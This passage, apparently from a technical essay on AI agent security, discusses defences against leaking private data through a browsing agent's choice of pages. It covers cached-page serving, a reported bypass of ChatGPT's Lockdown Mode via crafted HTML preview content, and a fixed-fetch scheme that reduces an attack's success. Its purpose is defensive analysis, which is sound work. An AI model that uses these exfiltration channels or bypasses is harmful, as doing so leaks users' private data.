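Serving stored copies of pages keeps even a yes-or-no answer from leaking, because the attacker receives no request whichever page the model chooses. The channel therefore carries log₂ 1, or zero, bits. This protection covers only requests served from the stored copies. ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode limits browsing to cached pages, but The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) reports that a flaw in ChatGPT's HTML preview let crafted content bypass the mode's restrictions. OpenAI has patched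 the flaw.

When an agent needs live pages, Liang and colleagues propose hiding its choice by having software fetch a fixed number of pages, selected without using private data. The agent then chooses among the local copies. This lowered the attack's F1 score from 0.89 to 0.39, but the attacker still recovered some of the concepts. It also multiplies the traffic, because completely hiding a choice among 36 pages requires fetching all 36.
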